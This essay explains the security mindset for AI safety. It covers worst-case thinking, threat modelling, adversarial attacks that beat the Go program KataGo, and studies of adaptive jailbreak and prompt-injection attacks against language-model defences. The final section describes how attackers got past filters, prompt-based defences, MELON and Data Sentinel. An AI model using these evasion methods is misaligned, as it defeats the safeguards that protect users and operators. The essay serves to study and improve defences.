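# The security mindset in AI safety: designing AI systems for adversaries instead of typical cases

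## What the security mindset is and how it differs from testing on typical cases

The security mindset is the habit, taken from computer security, of asking how someone could make a system fail and which assumptions its safety rests on. Most engineers instead ask whether a system works under the conditions it will usually meet, and they test it on a sample of those conditions. AI developers have largely done the same, running a model on a benchmark (a fixed set of test questions) and reporting the share of right answers. That figure is a fair guide to ordinary use, but it poorly predicts what happens when someone looks for questions the model gets wrong. People have more to gain from finding such failures now that AI systems read email, run code and spend money for their users.

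Bruce Schneier, a cryptographer and writer on security, popularised the term in a 2008 essay, *The Security Mindset*. His first example is a toy ant farm that comes with a card on which the buyer writes an address, and the company then mails the ants there. A friend of Schneier's was surprised that ants could be sent by mail, but Schneier was more interested that the company would send a tube of live ants to anyone he named. His second example is SmartWater, a liquid with an identifier unique to its owner, who paints it on valuables to prove ownership. Schneier thought of painting his own SmartWater on someone else's valuables and then calling the police.

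In both stories, the system works as its designers wanted: the ant company mails ants, and the liquid identifies an owner. The trouble comes from an input the designers hadn't imagined. Schneier thinks this oversight is normal for engineers, whose job is to think about how to make things work. He believes that noticing how to make them fail takes a different mindset.

Eliezer Yudkowsky, co-founder of the Machine Intelligence Research Institute (MIRI), divides the security mindset into two parts in MIRI's 2017 fictional dialogue *Security Mindset and Ordinary Paranoia*. The easier part, which he calls ordinary paranoia, is imagining attacks, including clever ones, and blocking each of them, which plenty of programmers can do. The harder part is guarding against mistakes in one's own reasoning. Every secure system has a safety story, a set of factual assumptions that together imply the system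 is safe, and someone with the full mindset tries to rely on fewer assumptions.

### Removing assumptions: the password file

Yudkowsky's example is a computer that has to check passwords. The simplest way is to store the passwords in a list and compare what the user types against it, but anyone who reads the list can then log in as any user.

An ordinary paranoid imagines someone stealing the list of passwords and moves it to a protected part of the disk, behind special code. The argument that the system is safe now assumes that nobody can read this file. The security expert in Yudkowsky's dialogue would rather not make that assumption, however good the protection. The special code runs less often than the rest, so it is more likely to contain unnoticed bugs, and there may be a way to get data off the disk that bypasses it.

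The next idea is to encrypt the password file. But the computer must decrypt the file to check a password, so the key has to be stored on the same machine. Security now depends on the attacker not finding the key, instead of not reading the file. Someone might then suggest encrypting the key as well, and continuing until there are seven keys in seven hiding places.

The arithmetic for seven keys looks wonderful if one is careless. Suppose a thief has a 10% chance of finding any given key. If the seven chances were independent, the thief would get all of them with probability 0.1^7, or one in ten million. The correct rule is

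P(all seven) = P(first) × P(second, given the first) × … × P(seventh, given the first six)

and the later factors are nowhere near 10%. A thief who already has two of the keys has probably found a way to read the disk directly, and that way gives up the other five too. The answer stays close to 10%. It could even be worse, because every hiding place needs more code, and the bug that exposes the disk might be in the code that hides the fourth key.

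Security engineers instead use a one-way hash, a function h that is easy to compute but infeasible to reverse. When a user picks a password, the machine stores h(password) and discards the password. At each login, it applies h to what the user typed and compares the result with the stored value. A thief who copies the file gets only strings that the login screen will not accept. The file is as easy to read as before, but reading it no longer reveals the passwords, and the machine has no password-recovery procedure that an attacker could trick it into running.

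With a bare hash, two users who both chose "password" have identical entries, and an attacker can hash a dictionary of common passwords once and look up every account in every stolen file. So the machine also picks a random string for each user, called a salt, and stores it with h(salt + password). The attacker must now hash the dictionary again for each account, so attacking many accounts takes much more computation. An attacker who concentrates on one account can still quickly guess a password like "password".

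The story still relies on assumptions, such as that h is one-way and that nobody can read the machine's memory just after a user types. Yudkowsky would therefore still protect the file as a second line of defence. He accepts extra layers if the builder expects the first layer to hold by itself and the others do not make the system too complicated to understand. He also grants that a short story is not always a good one, since two true assumptions are better than a single false one.

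Another example from the same dialogue shows why he talks about assumptions more than about attackers. Companies used to send automatic email from made-up addresses at donotreply.com, a domain they did not own, assuming that replies would go nowhere. Then someone registered the domain and began to receive the replies, some with bank statements attached. A suspicious enough programmer might have foreseen this, but a programmer who disliked relying on that assumption would have avoided the problem without needing to foresee it.

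Organisations can spend years blocking individual attacks without fixing the flaw that allows them. *Security Mindset*, a 2022 essay on the forum LessWrong by a professional penetration tester, describes one such client. Every year the tester reported the same flaw, which let an outsider insert a script into a web page. The client responded each time with a more elaborate filter against the previous year's attack strings, and the tester then found a string that the filter missed. The proper repair was to encode user text on output so that browsers would never run it as code. The tester does not dismiss lists of known attacks, because the software industry needed a great many examples of this flaw before people understood the proper repair.

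### Average loss and maximum loss

The difference between testing on typical cases and designing for an adversary fits into two formulas. Let x be an input, L(x) the harm done when the system receives it, and p(x) the probability that x turns up in typical use. Then

average-case loss = Σ p(x) · L(x), summed over all inputs x

worst-case loss = max L(x), over all inputs x in A

where A is the set of inputs that an adversary can reach. Fixing A is the business of a threat model, a statement of what the adversary wants, knows and can do. The probability p(x) does not occur in the second formula. However rare an input is in ordinary use, it counts in full if the adversary can produce it.

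Qi, Huang and colleagues (2024) point out in *AI Risk Management Should Incorporate Both Safety and Security* that an attacker who controls the route to a fault can trigger it every time, even if chance would trigger it only one time in a million. They add that accident statistics stay useful because accidents of a given kind keep happening at roughly the same rate, whereas attackers change their methods when the old ones stop working. This is a reason to distrust any probability of attack drawn from past records, but not to discard average-case results. Qi and colleagues note that training a model to decline harmful requests reduces accidental harm even where a determined attacker can get round it, and they want evaluators to judge such measures separately against accidents and against attacks.

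Sampling can also estimate the average, with more accuracy as the sample grows, but it does not work for the worst case. Each successful attack shows that the worst case is at least that bad, and a failed search for attacks leaves open whether a worse one exists. This is why Navaie (2026), in *Epistemic Norms for AI Safety and Alignment Research*, holds that a benchmark score of 99.9% is less informative than the 0.1% of cases that failed. Navaie also looked at ten papers on AI alignment, the problem of keeping capable systems' goals and behaviour acceptable to people, and found worst-case or adversarial results in four. Navaie presents this as a pilot, and ten papers read by one person are very thin evidence about a field.

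Yudkowsky has an example that shows how far apart the two losses can be. A program accepts one kilobyte of input per session. That is 8,000 bits, so there are 2^8000 possible inputs, or about 10^2408. Suppose that a googol of them, 10^100, make the program misbehave. This is far more than the number of atoms in the observable universe, and yet the chance that a random input is among them is

10^100 / 10^2408 = 10^−2308

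Suppose a tester feeds in a billion random inputs a second for 10^18 seconds, more than twice the present age of the universe. The expected number of misbehaviours among those 10^27 inputs is 10^27 × 10^−2308, or 10^−2281, so the tester will almost certainly never see one. If misbehaviour counts as a loss of 1 and everything else as 0, the average loss on random inputs is 10^−2308, but the worst-case loss is 1.

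An attacker who searches for the fault may do much better than the tester. Suppose the fault occurs only when 958 of the thousand bytes have exact values, while the other 42 can be anything, so roughly a googol of inputs trigger it. Suppose also that the program checks those 958 bytes in order and takes slightly longer to answer whenever one more of them is right. With a good clock, the attacker can then find the first byte in at most 256 tries, the second in at most 256 more, and so on, reaching the fault in fewer than 250,000 tries. At a billion tries a second, that takes less than a quarter of a millisecond. Someone who has read the program's code may need only one try. Without the timing clue, the code or some other hint, the attacker does no better than the tester.

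The damage comes from a search guided by some feedback, and malice is only the most common reason for running one. Yudkowsky likewise says that the optimisation matters more than the adversary. Optimisation pressure here means any systematic search for outcomes that score well, and it can push a system into states that chance would never reach. His later conclusions about superintelligent AI start from this idea.

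The standard assumption is that the attacker knows the design. This is Kerckhoffs's principle, named after Auguste Kerckhoffs, who wrote in 1883 that a military cipher should stay safe even if the enemy captures the whole apparatus, so long as the key stays secret. Designs leak because employees change jobs and anyone can buy a product and take it apart. A leaked design may also take years to replace, whereas a leaked key takes minutes. For an AI model whose developer has published its weights (the numbers that training produced), the assumption is true. Designers may still keep a design secret, but they should not rely on its secrecy. Seven hidden keys fail this test, but the hashed password file passes because everyone knows how the common hash functions work and that knowledge makes the file no easier to reverse.

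Taking a maximum also gives the attacker an advantage. A defender has to establish that every input in A is harmless to show that the worst-case loss is low, while an attacker needs only one harmful input to show that it is high. A team that closes ninety-nine holes out of a hundred may have greatly reduced its average loss, but an attacker who knows about the remaining hole can exploit it as easily as before.

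### Small failure rates and repeated tries

Attackers can also try again. Take a jailbreak, an input by which a user gets a model to do what its developer trained it to refuse, and suppose that it works 1% of the time. A benchmark would record 99% resistance. The probability that 100 independent tries all fail is 0.99^100, about 0.37, so the probability that at least one succeeds is

1 − (0.99)^100 ≈ 0.63

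or 63%. With 300 tries it is 95%. A developer who wanted to hold an attacker with 100 tries to a 1% chance overall would need to bring the success rate per try down to about one in ten thousand.

The calculation assumes that the tries are independent, but real tries are only partly independent. Language models choose their words with some randomness, so a prompt that fails once may work the next time. But if a filter blocks the prompt for a fixed reason, repeating it won't help, and 63% is too high. The figure is probably too low if the attacker learns from each refusal and rewrites the prompt, as in adaptive attacks on language models.

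Repetition matters without any attacker, too. Kelly, Kementsietsidis and colleagues (2026), in *Humanity's First Exam*, tested 18 models on 544 questions that people find easy, such as how many of the coffee mugs at the front of a picture have no steam rising from them. The questions come in 136 families of four: an original and three variants with, say, different names or a different layout. The Google team put each question to each model six times. If c of n answers are right, then for k answers drawn from the n,

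P(at least one of k is right) = 1 − C(n − c, k) / C(n, k)

P(all k are right) = C(c, k) / C(n, k)

where C(a, b) is the number of ways to choose b things from a. A model that gets five of its six answers right scores 83% on a single try. With k = 4 it scores 100% by the first formula and 5/15, or 33%, by the second. For a whole family, the team multiplied the four "all right" scores together, which gives the chance that sixteen answers in a row are correct.

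The five best models scored between 96% and 98% on single tries. When all sixteen answers in a family had to be right, they averaged 86%, ranging from 80.5% to 92.4%. Small differences between models also grew. Claude Opus 5.5 was 6.6 points behind GPT-6.2 Astra on single tries and 29.4 points behind on whole families.

If the top five models' errors had been independent, their average accuracy of about 97% per try would have given them roughly a 60% chance of getting all sixteen tries right. They did better because their errors cluster on particular questions. Each model gets most questions right nearly every time and some wrong nearly every time. Different models also often miss the same question. In one family of four questions about spatial relations, 15 of the 18 models failed on the same variant, which drew 78 wrong answers out of 108, while the other three drew 11 in total. Clustered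 errors are more worrying than random ones when a system faces attackers, because random errors are hard to exploit, while an attacker who finds a question that reliably defeats a model can use it again.

*Humanity's First Exam* provides evidence about models' consistency, not their security, because nobody was searching for inputs to beat the models under test. Kelly and colleagues kept a question only if at least one of a panel of earlier models got it wrong, so the scores are probably lower than they would be in ordinary use. Sixteen of the 18 models tested came out after the questions were collected, which limits how closely the questions could fit those models' weaknesses. Individual human raters answered 91% of the original questions correctly, below the best models' single-try scores on the full set. The results show that a model can score in the high nineties on a single try and still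 almost never get certain questions right, and an adversary would seek out those questions.

### Advice that people can follow

Adam Shostack, who ran threat modelling (the systematic search for what could go wrong with a design) at Microsoft, thinks it is bad advice to tell every engineer to think like an attacker. In *Think Like An Attacker?*, a post on the Shostack + Friends Blog, he wrote that most people have no idea how to do it and do not know what attackers want or how they approach a problem. To illustrate the difficulty, he suggests trying to think like a professional chef and asking how you would plan the menu or get a hundred dinners out in an hour. In *Experiences Threat Modeling at Microsoft* (2008), he reported that the phrase had meant nothing to many engineers there, and that they were reluctant to admit it because everyone made it sound so natural. In *"Think Like an Attacker"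 is an opt-in mistake*, he recalls a developer who told him in 2006, swearing heavily, that if there was time to read a book about attackers, then Shostack could write the features that customers were paying for.

A second complaint is that people who do try to imitate attackers may guess wrong. In a review of Shostack's book on threat modelling, the IAPP, an association of privacy professionals, quotes his warning that this approach "may lead you to focus on the wrong threats."

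John Kelsey, a former security consultant, defended the slogan "think like an attacker" in the comments under Shostack's first post. He wrote that designers like their systems and spend their time thinking of reasons why attacks are impossible. He had often found serious holes by sitting down with a designer and asking "why can't I do X?" two or three times. The designer usually knew enough to find the hole but had not been looking for it. Shostack replied in *The Discipline of "think like an attacker"* (2008) that he agreed with the aim. He called the problem creator-blindness and doubted that urging people to think differently would fix it.

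Shostack would teach a procedure that begins with something engineers do know, their own design. In the version Microsoft used in 2008, a team first draws the system as a diagram of processes, data stores, data flows and outside parties, and marks the trust boundaries, where data passes between parts with different privileges. The team then checks each element against the STRIDE list of threats: spoofing, tampering, repudiation (someone denying what they did), information disclosure, denial of service and elevation of privilege. Finally, it mitigates the threats and checks the result. Shostack ranked redesign first among the mitigations, ahead of adding a standard protection. This is close to Yudkowsky's preference for removing the assumption, but as part of a procedure that an ordinary team can follow.

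He has since boiled the method down to four questions, which Shostack (2024), in *Understanding The Four-Question Framework for Threat Modeling*, explains almost word by word:

- What are we working on? This keeps a team on the part it can still change, where "what are we building?" would invite it to reopen everything.
- What can go wrong? The wording is loose on purpose, so that people without security jargon can answer.
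- What are we going to do about it? Fixing the problem is one answer. Dropping the feature or accepting the risk are others.
- Did we do a good job? The team asks whether the exercise found real problems and whether it was worth the time.

Schneier and Yudkowsky are both more pessimistic about teaching the mindset. Schneier suspects that it is far easier to teach someone cryptography, although he was interested in Tadayoshi Kohno's attempt to teach the mindset in an undergraduate course at the University of Washington. *Security Mindset*, written by a tester, reports that the mindset was hard to cultivate in most engineers. The tester settled for one or two "champions" per team and a rule that every planned feature needed three "abuser stories" about how someone might misuse it, such as a customer trying to pay minus $100. All of this is testimony from practitioners, none of whom ran a trial,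 and Shostack claims only that his method is useful, not that it is right.

His objection applies to ordinary paranoia, which depends on picturing attackers, but much less to the habit of questioning assumptions. His own remedy, the STRIDE procedure, grew out of an analysis of known software flaws, so it works best on systems like the ones that had those flaws. Language models do not resemble them much, and Shostack (2026), in *PHANTOM-B*, offers a new list for them. Its eight prompts include prompt injection (instructions planted by a third party in material that a model reads, which the model then follows), hallucination, over-reliance on the model, and bias. He wrote it for people who build products on top of a language model and left out the threats that concern those who train one. He also warns that the best defences now available for these models are probabilistic, so a developer who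 adopts one still has to ask how many tries an attacker will get.

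## Superhuman Go programs that lose to weak opponents

Researchers trained a program specifically to beat KataGo, the strongest Go program that anyone can download, which plays far better than any human. Their program won more than 97% of its games against KataGo, even though human amateurs can beat their program.

### How KataGo chooses a move

In Go, Black and White take turns placing stones on the intersections of a 19 by 19 grid. Stones of the same colour that touch along the lines form a group, and the empty points next to a group are its liberties. A player who fills a group's last liberty captures the group and removes its stones from the board. Whoever controls more of the board at the end wins. Players call a group dead when it can no longer avoid capture, and they often leave dead stones on the board because capturing them seems to make no difference to the result.

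KataGo, which David Wu published in 2019, combines a neural network with a search. Given a position, the network produces a probability for each possible next move and an estimate of the chance of winning. The search then follows a line of moves from the current position. In the standard version of this method, it takes at each step the move a with the highest

Q(a) + c · P(a) · √N / (1 + N(a))

where Q(a) is the average estimate found so far after move a, P(a) is the network's probability for that move, N(a) is how often the search has tried it, N is the total number of tries from that position, and c is a constant. When the line reaches a new position, the network evaluates it, and the result enters the averages of all the moves that led there. Each such pass is a visit. Once the visits run out, the program plays the move it has tried most.

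Wang, Gleave and colleagues (2023), in *Adversarial Policies Beat Superhuman Go AIs*, estimate that KataGo plays like a weak professional without search and better than any human when it searches with more than about 128 visits per move. KataGo learned by playing against itself, so nearly all the positions it trained on came from games between two copies of KataGo.

### Training a program to beat one opponent

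Wang and colleagues froze KataGo and trained a second program solely to beat it. This attacker could only place stones or pass, like any player. The researchers could run KataGo's network on any position but did not use its weights. A normal Go program looks ahead by assuming that its opponent plays as it would, but the attacker used KataGo's network to predict KataGo's replies. The attacker started from random weights and would have lost every game against the full program, so it trained first against early, weak versions of KataGo, then against later versions, and then against KataGo with more search, up to 131,072 visits a move.

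The first attacker got KataGo to pass too early, while stray enemy stones still kept KataGo's territory from counting under the computer rules KataGo had trained on. The attacker won 99.9% of games against KataGo without search. The researchers then added a rule that stopped KataGo from passing early, and the attacker lost all 1,000 games it played.

The researchers repeated the training against the patched program and got a second attacker, which won in the middle of the game. Training it took 14% of the computation used to train KataGo. Against the unpatched KataGo at 4,096 visits, it won 97.3% of 1,000 games. At ten million visits, which take over an hour per move on good consumer hardware, it still won 72% of 50 games. The same attacker ranked at about 17 kyu, a beginner's grade, on a public Go server, so its wins over KataGo did not come from playing Go well in general.

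The team's Go expert went through a typical game, in which KataGo played Black with 1,600 visits a move:

1. The attacker opened so badly that KataGo's estimate of its own chances passed 90% before move 10.
2. From move 20, the attacker built a small group in one quarter of the board that any player would call dead. KataGo's stones came to surround it and joined up into a ring.
3. From move 74, the attacker slowly surrounded the ring from outside. This took more than 100 moves, during which KataGo could have saved the ring with simple moves.
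4. Move 189 closed the last way out. KataGo lost the whole ring and with it the game.

The expert thought that someone who had played for a few months might have found a saving move. In games like this one, KataGo's estimated chance of winning typically stays above 99% for most of the game and often collapses only one move before the capture.

Wu suggested that networks like KataGo's misjudge groups that form a ring, which are very rare in normal games. Wang and colleagues tested this by changing one or two stones to break the ring while keeping the best moves and the fate of every group the same. Many versions of KataGo evaluated the original and altered boards very differently, which is good evidence that the ring itself causes the error.

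Wu already knew about the weakness. Posting as lightvector in the Go forum thread *Kellin Pelrine Beats AI*, Wu dated its discovery to about 2020 or 2021 and recalled finding it in other programs too. But as far as Wang and colleagues know, nobody had used it to win games. The flaw almost never came up in normal play, so it looked harmless until a search found a way to bring it up in nearly every game.

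More search helps KataGo only partly, because the search averages estimates from the same mistaken network until it reads as far as the capture. In ten positions where KataGo had made its losing move with 1,600 visits, it found a winning move in eight when given 500,000. However, attackers trained against more search learned to set longer traps. The capture came an average of 6.4 moves after KataGo's last chance in games with less search, and 8.4 moves after it in games with more. Even if the search had to consider only five moves at each turn, two extra moves would multiply the number of lines to read by 25. KataGo chose a losing move in all five positions where it was tested with a billion visits, which came from games it had lost at a million.

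The attacker also won a few games against programs it had never played before, 6.1% against Leela Zero and 3.5% against ELF OpenGo. The expert, Kellin Pelrine, learned the method from the attacker's games and, without a computer's help, beat a KataGo bot on a public server in 14 games out of 15. Pelrine also won after giving the bot nine extra stones at the start, a handicap that would let a human professional beat practically anyone. Other players have since beaten several programs the same way, including FineArt, whose code is not public.

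### Three attempts at a defence

In December 2022, Wu began to repair KataGo with adversarial training, which trains a system on attacks so that it learns to withstand them. KataGo started 0.08% of its practice games from hand-picked positions with a ring under attack. By May 2023, the original attacker hardly ever won. Wang and colleagues then trained the attacker further against the repaired version, and it won 47% of games at 4,096 visits.

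Some of the same researchers then asked whether a more determined effort could succeed. In *Can Go AIs Be Adversarially Robust?*, Tseng, McLean and colleagues (2024) tested later versions of Wu's repair and two defences of their own, training new attackers against each. The table gives their results. The 27% figure comes from *Beyond the Board*, the team's account for general readers.

| Defended program | Attacker | Visits per move | Attacker's wins |
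|---|---|---|---|
| Hand-made positions, December 2023 | "Gift" attack | 512 | 91% |
| Hand-made positions, December 2023 | Ring attack | 4,096 | 65% |
| Hand-made positions, December 2023 | Ring attack | 65,536 | 27% |
| Hand-made positions, May 2024 | Larger ring | 65,536 | 56% |
| Nine rounds of training | Attacker from the ninth round | 65,536 | 42% |
| Nine rounds of training | Separately trained attacker | 512 | 81% |
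| Nine rounds of training | Separately trained attacker | 4,096 | 4% |
| Transformer network | Retrained ring attack | 65,536 | 78% |

The hand-made positions stopped the original attacker completely, but one of the new attackers used a trick that involves no ring, called the gift attack. KataGo needlessly lets the attacker take two stones and then needs to take one back, which the rule against repeating an earlier position forbids, so a dead group of the attacker's comes back to life. The blunder is odd because KataGo's network receives an input that marks the moves this rule forbids. Wu added positions from the new attacks in February 2024, but the May 2024 version lost to a bigger, oblong ring.

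In each round of the second defence, iterated adversarial training, Tseng and colleagues trained the defender against the latest attacker, then trained the attacker against the improved defender. The defender played 18% of its training games against the attacker and the rest against itself. After nine rounds, it lost only a few percent of games to the attackers it had trained against. But the ninth attacker, which was trained further from the eighth, won 42% of games against it at 65,536 visits. Training that attacker took 26% as much computation as the defender's entire training.

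Every attacker in the series relied on a ring. The rings differed in size, location and the stones inside them, but humans find them all about equally easy to deal with. The defender had learned to handle particular rings but not to judge rings in general. The nine rounds still helped somewhat. An attacker trained without access to the earlier rounds easily beat the defender at 512 visits but almost never at 4,096, where the original attacker had beaten the original KataGo decisively.

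The third defence tested Wu's suspicion that KataGo's type of network was part of the problem. The network is convolutional, meaning that it combines information from small neighbourhoods of the board, so it might have learned a local rule for judging groups that fails on large ones. Tseng and colleagues trained a new program on a transformer, which lets every part of the board directly influence every other. At 32,768 visits, it played at the level of top humans. At twice as many visits, it lost 78% of games to a retrained attacker, and at 512 visits it lost 2.5% even to the original attacker. A much deeper transformer might do better, but convolution is evidently not the whole cause. The team now suspects self-play, because a program that plays only copies of itself faces opponents with the same blind spots, which don't exploit its mistakes.

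More hopefully, they also report that defending against any fixed attack took little computation. Over the nine rounds, finding attacks took 18 times as much computation as training the defender to beat them. (The 26% above is a share of a total that includes KataGo's original training.) They think that faster ways of generating attacks might let a defender train on enough of them to become fully robust. This is a reasonable hope, but nothing in the ninth attacker's results suggests that effective rings were running out.

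### Whether capability brings robustness

KataGo's losses show that a system can be extremely skilled in typical cases and still fail in the worst case, so developers cannot make systems secure simply by making them more capable. Research on language models suggests that more skill often helps a little, though unreliably.

The cleanest comparisons are between models of different sizes trained in the same way. *Scaling Trends in Language Model Robustness* (Howe, McKenzie and colleagues, 2024) compares models with 7.6 million to about 12 billion parameters, the adjustable numbers inside a network. The models did simple text classification tasks, and the attacks added a short string of text to turn a right answer into a wrong one. On film reviews, one attack succeeded almost every time against the smallest model and less than 20% of the time against the largest. On spam detection, a model over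 fifty times larger than another was easier to fool, and on a task about word length, size made no difference.

Adversarial training helped models of every size. But when attacker and defender both doubled their computation, the attacker benefited more. This advantage shrank as models grew, and Howe and colleagues think it might reverse if the trend continues well beyond the sizes they tested.

Size may also protect against one kind of attack and not another. *Risk Under Pressure* (2026) compared models of 0.5 to 7 billion parameters by how much an attacker gains per unit of computation. The larger size cut that gain almost twentyfold for an attack that needs heavy computation, but only 2.6-fold for one that needs little. Attackers can be expected to choose the second. In *Unifying Adversarial Robustness and Training Across Text Scoring Models* (2026), the middle-sized of three reward models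 (which score other models' answers during training) was generally the hardest to fool.

Released models are harder to compare because their developers put different amounts of work into defences. *Security Challenges in AI Agent Deployment* (2025) describes a public contest in which almost 2,000 people made 1.8 million attempts to get 22 models to break their rules. They succeeded against every model on every type of violation. The UK AI Security Institute's *Frontier AI Trends Report* compares robustness in this contest with scores on a science test and finds R² = 0.097, so a linear fit explains under 10% of the variation between models. Xander Davies of the institute pointed out in a talk, *State of Jailbreaks* (2025), that the slope is positive. He credits most of the recent gains to companies' deliberate investment. The institute's experts needed 10 minutes to find a jailbreak for biological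 misuse in one model and over 7 hours in another released six months later.

A newer model can be more vulnerable to attack than an older one. In *Measuring the Residual Jailbreak Surface of Frontier Large Language Models* (2026), two kinds of automated attack succeeded in 2.7% of cases against Anthropic's Fable 5, 5.8% against the older Opus 4.8, and 8.2% against Fable 5.1, the newest of the three.

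The best recent evidence that capability helps comes from agents, AI systems that act through tools such as a browser. In *CAVEAT*, Li, Epperson and colleagues (2026) sent agents to buy the best product for a user in simulated online shops that pushed other products through sponsored placement, late fees and similar devices. With little reasoning, the three sizes of GPT-5.6 bought the right product in 0%, 11.7% and 51.7% of cases. With more reasoning, the largest reached 90%. When the catalogue had 2,112 products, the largest model chose correctly 90% of the time in a neutral shop but never in 50 tries in a shop that steered buyers, where it stopped at the first of 88 pages of results every time. Instructions to settle the user's aims before browsing and to check the decision before buying raised its success rate to 80%. A real attacker would presumably do more than a shop that promotes its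 own favourites.

Xu, Han and colleagues (2026), in *AgentPerturb*, found a similar pattern with plain noise, such as missing instructions or wrong tool descriptions. The three most capable of ten models lost less than half as much performance as the others on average, but the overall link between capability and performance loss was weak and not statistically significant. Two DeepSeek models one point apart on a capability index lost 4.4% and 46.6% of their scores on the same set of office tasks. A model can also appear safe because it is weak. *Governing Execution Risk in Agentic AI Systems* (2026) found low risk in very small agents partly because they could not carry out the tasks an attacker set them.

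Extra reasoning time is the closest equivalent in language models to extra visits in KataGo, and it has a similar effect. In *Trading Inference-Time Compute for Adversarial Robustness*, Zaremba, Nitishinskaya and colleagues (2025) gave two OpenAI models more time to reason, and in many cases the share of successful attacks fell towards zero, with important exceptions. In *Does More Inference-Time Compute Really Help Robustness?*, Wu and Xiang (2025) found the same benefit in smaller models, but more reasoning made the models less robust when the attacker could read it.

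### How far a frozen game program stands for deployed systems

Tseng and colleagues chose Go because the game should favour the defender. An attacker has only a few hundred legal moves each turn, the program is far above human level, and playing well against attackers doesn't have to conflict with playing well in general. A language model that reads arbitrary text has none of these advantages.

Other features of the experiments favour the attacker. The ring attacker played about a million training games against copies of KataGo that never adapted to its attacks. A company that runs a model on its own servers could notice such an attack, ban the accounts and change the model. A deployed system can also refuse a request or call in a person, whereas KataGo has to make a move. And if self-play is the cause, the flaw may not carry over to language models, which learn largely from human text. Wang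 and colleagues acknowledge that Go programs may be unusually vulnerable.

Patching is the most important of these differences, and the Go results provide some evidence about it. Wu patched KataGo repeatedly, and each time the researchers found a new attack on the patched version. They did not test a defender that keeps changing while the attacker is still learning, though Tseng and colleagues suggest trying one. Such a defence might do much better, but it would not stop an attacker who practises elsewhere, as Pelrine did by studying recorded games. Attacks from the public contest also worked on models that had not taken part in it. Patches make attacks harder to find and shorter-lived, which is very useful to a company with a hosted model. They do not protect copies of an open-weight model that people have already downloaded, which stay fixed, as KataGo did during the experiments.

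The Go case supports a modest requirement that developers measure worst-case robustness separately from skill for every new version. Tseng and colleagues suggest measuring whether an attacker can provoke losing blunders that a person would avoid, how much computation it takes to train a successful attacker, and how far extra computation at run time reduces the vulnerability. The attacker also has to be retrained against each new version. Wang and colleagues' original attack program won no games against a version of KataGo trained on hand-made positions, but it won 92% after further training against that version, using 8% as much computation as the defence.

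## Twelve defences for language models under attacks designed to beat them

Training KataGo on known attacks protected it only until someone trained a new attacker, and defences for language models have the same weakness. In *The Attacker Moves Second*, Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) attacked twelve recent defences with methods adapted to each. Most of the developers had reported attack success rates near zero, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences. The team, which included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, presented the work at USENIX Security in 2026.

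Some of the twelve defences are meant to stop jailbreaks by users, and the others are meant to stop prompt injection by third parties. Their developers had usually run a static test, which uses a fixed list of attacks that had worked on earlier models. Some had also run a general-purpose attack program, but with little computation and without adapting it to the defence.

### How the attacks work

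Nasr and colleagues consider attackers with three levels of access. The strongest has the model's weights and can calculate how any change to the input would affect the output. A weaker one can only send inputs but sees the probabilities the model assigns to possible words. The weakest sees only the finished text. Following Kerckhoffs's principle, the team assumes attackers know how the defence works. The team also gives them plenty of computing power, because it wants to learn whether an attacker could break each defence at all.

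Every attack runs the same loop. It proposes some inputs, scores how close each came to succeeding, keeps the best and uses them to produce new ones. The team ran this loop in four ways:

- Gradient methods use the weights to calculate which changes of wording would most raise the chance of the desired output. They are unreliable on text, because a word cannot change by a tiny amount, and the team used them against only one defence.
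- In reinforcement learning, a second language model writes the attacks, and training rewards it for those that score well.
- In the search method, a language model rewrites promising earlier attempts and another model marks the results out of ten. The program keeps a varied pool of attempts so that it does not just polish one idea. It had up to 800 tries at each task.
- In a public contest, people wrote attacks by hand.

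For each defence, the team chose the attack methods it expected to work best and largely kept the test that the defence's developers had used. The results therefore do not rank the twelve defences against each other.

### Four kinds of defence

Three of the defences change the prompt. Spotlighting uses special markers to separate trusted text from the rest. RPO adds text optimised against known jailbreaks. Prompt Sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text to keep the model focused on it. Attackers commonly got round Prompt Sandwiching by presenting their own task as a step the model had to complete before it could finish the user's task, which repeating the request does nothing to prevent.

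Circuit Breakers, StruQ and MetaSecAlign train the model on examples of attacks. Most of the attacks that beat them imitated instructions from the system's operator. Nasr and colleagues compare these defences with research on image classifiers, where training on a fixed set of attacks also failed. Adversarial training worked there only when it generated new attacks throughout training, and it protected only against the type of attack it used.

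Protect AI's detector, PromptGuard, PIGuard and Google's Model Armor are separate classifiers that filter what goes into or comes out of the model and block anything suspicious. The attacks that got past them often looked like ordinary office procedure. A filter strict enough to catch those attacks would also block a lot of normal text, and some of these filters already block too much. Gemini 2.5 Pro completed 74% of ordinary tasks without a filter and 39% with either PIGuard or Protect AI's detector.

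The last two defences depend on something the attacker supposedly does not know. Data Sentinel prompts a model to repeat a secret key while ignoring the incoming text, and treats the text as an attack if the model fails. The team's attacker got past it by redefining the task in innocent-looking terms. MELON runs an agent twice, the second time with the user's request replaced by a harmless request for a summary. If the agent takes the same actions both times, the text presumably caused them, not the user's request. On Llama 3.3, the search program beat MELON in 76% of cases without a description of how it worked. Once the researchers added that description, the program found instructions that took effect only during the run with the user's request, and its success rate rose to 95%.

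Eight of the twelve defences protect agents from prompt injection. The team tested them on 80 tasks from AgentDojo, a simulated workplace where an agent handles things like email, calendars and travel bookings. Each cell in the table gives the success rate of one standard attack template, followed by that of the adaptive search. MetaSecAlign is a version of Llama 3.3 trained to resist injection. It has its own column because, as a model, it can be combined with the other defences.

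| Added defence | Gemini 2.5 Pro | GPT-5 Mini | Llama 3.3 70B | MetaSecAlign 70B |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% / 100% | 0% / 75% | 35% / 100% | 5% / 96% |
| Spotlighting | 28% / 99% | 0% / 47% | 28% / 99% | 1% / 99% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | 21% / 95% | 0% / 69% | 25% / 100% | 4% / 99% |
| Protect AI | 15% / 90% | 0% / 81% | 31% / 94% | 6% / 94% |
| PIGuard | 0% / 71% | 0% / 49% | 1% / 61% | 0% / 64% |
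| PromptGuard | 26% / 94% | 0% / 75% | 35% / 99% | 4% / 95% |
| Model Armor | 28% / 90% | 0% / 56% | 33% / 82% | 4% / 82% |
| MELON | 0% / 89% | 0% / 71% | 23% / 95% | 0% / 84% |

MetaSecAlign's developers had reported that AgentDojo's static attacks succeeded 2% of the time, close to the 5% found here. The search raised the rate to 96%. On the other four defences' own tests, attacks succeeded in 96% to 98% of cases against RPO and in every case against Circuit Breakers and StruQ. Against Data Sentinel, the attacker got the model to do a different task from the one assigned, with over 80% accuracy.

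The 1% for Spotlighting comes from a model already trained with MetaSecAlign. On Gemini 2.5 Pro, Spotlighting lowered the success rate of static attacks only from 30% to 28%, so even static tests gave little reason to trust it on that model.

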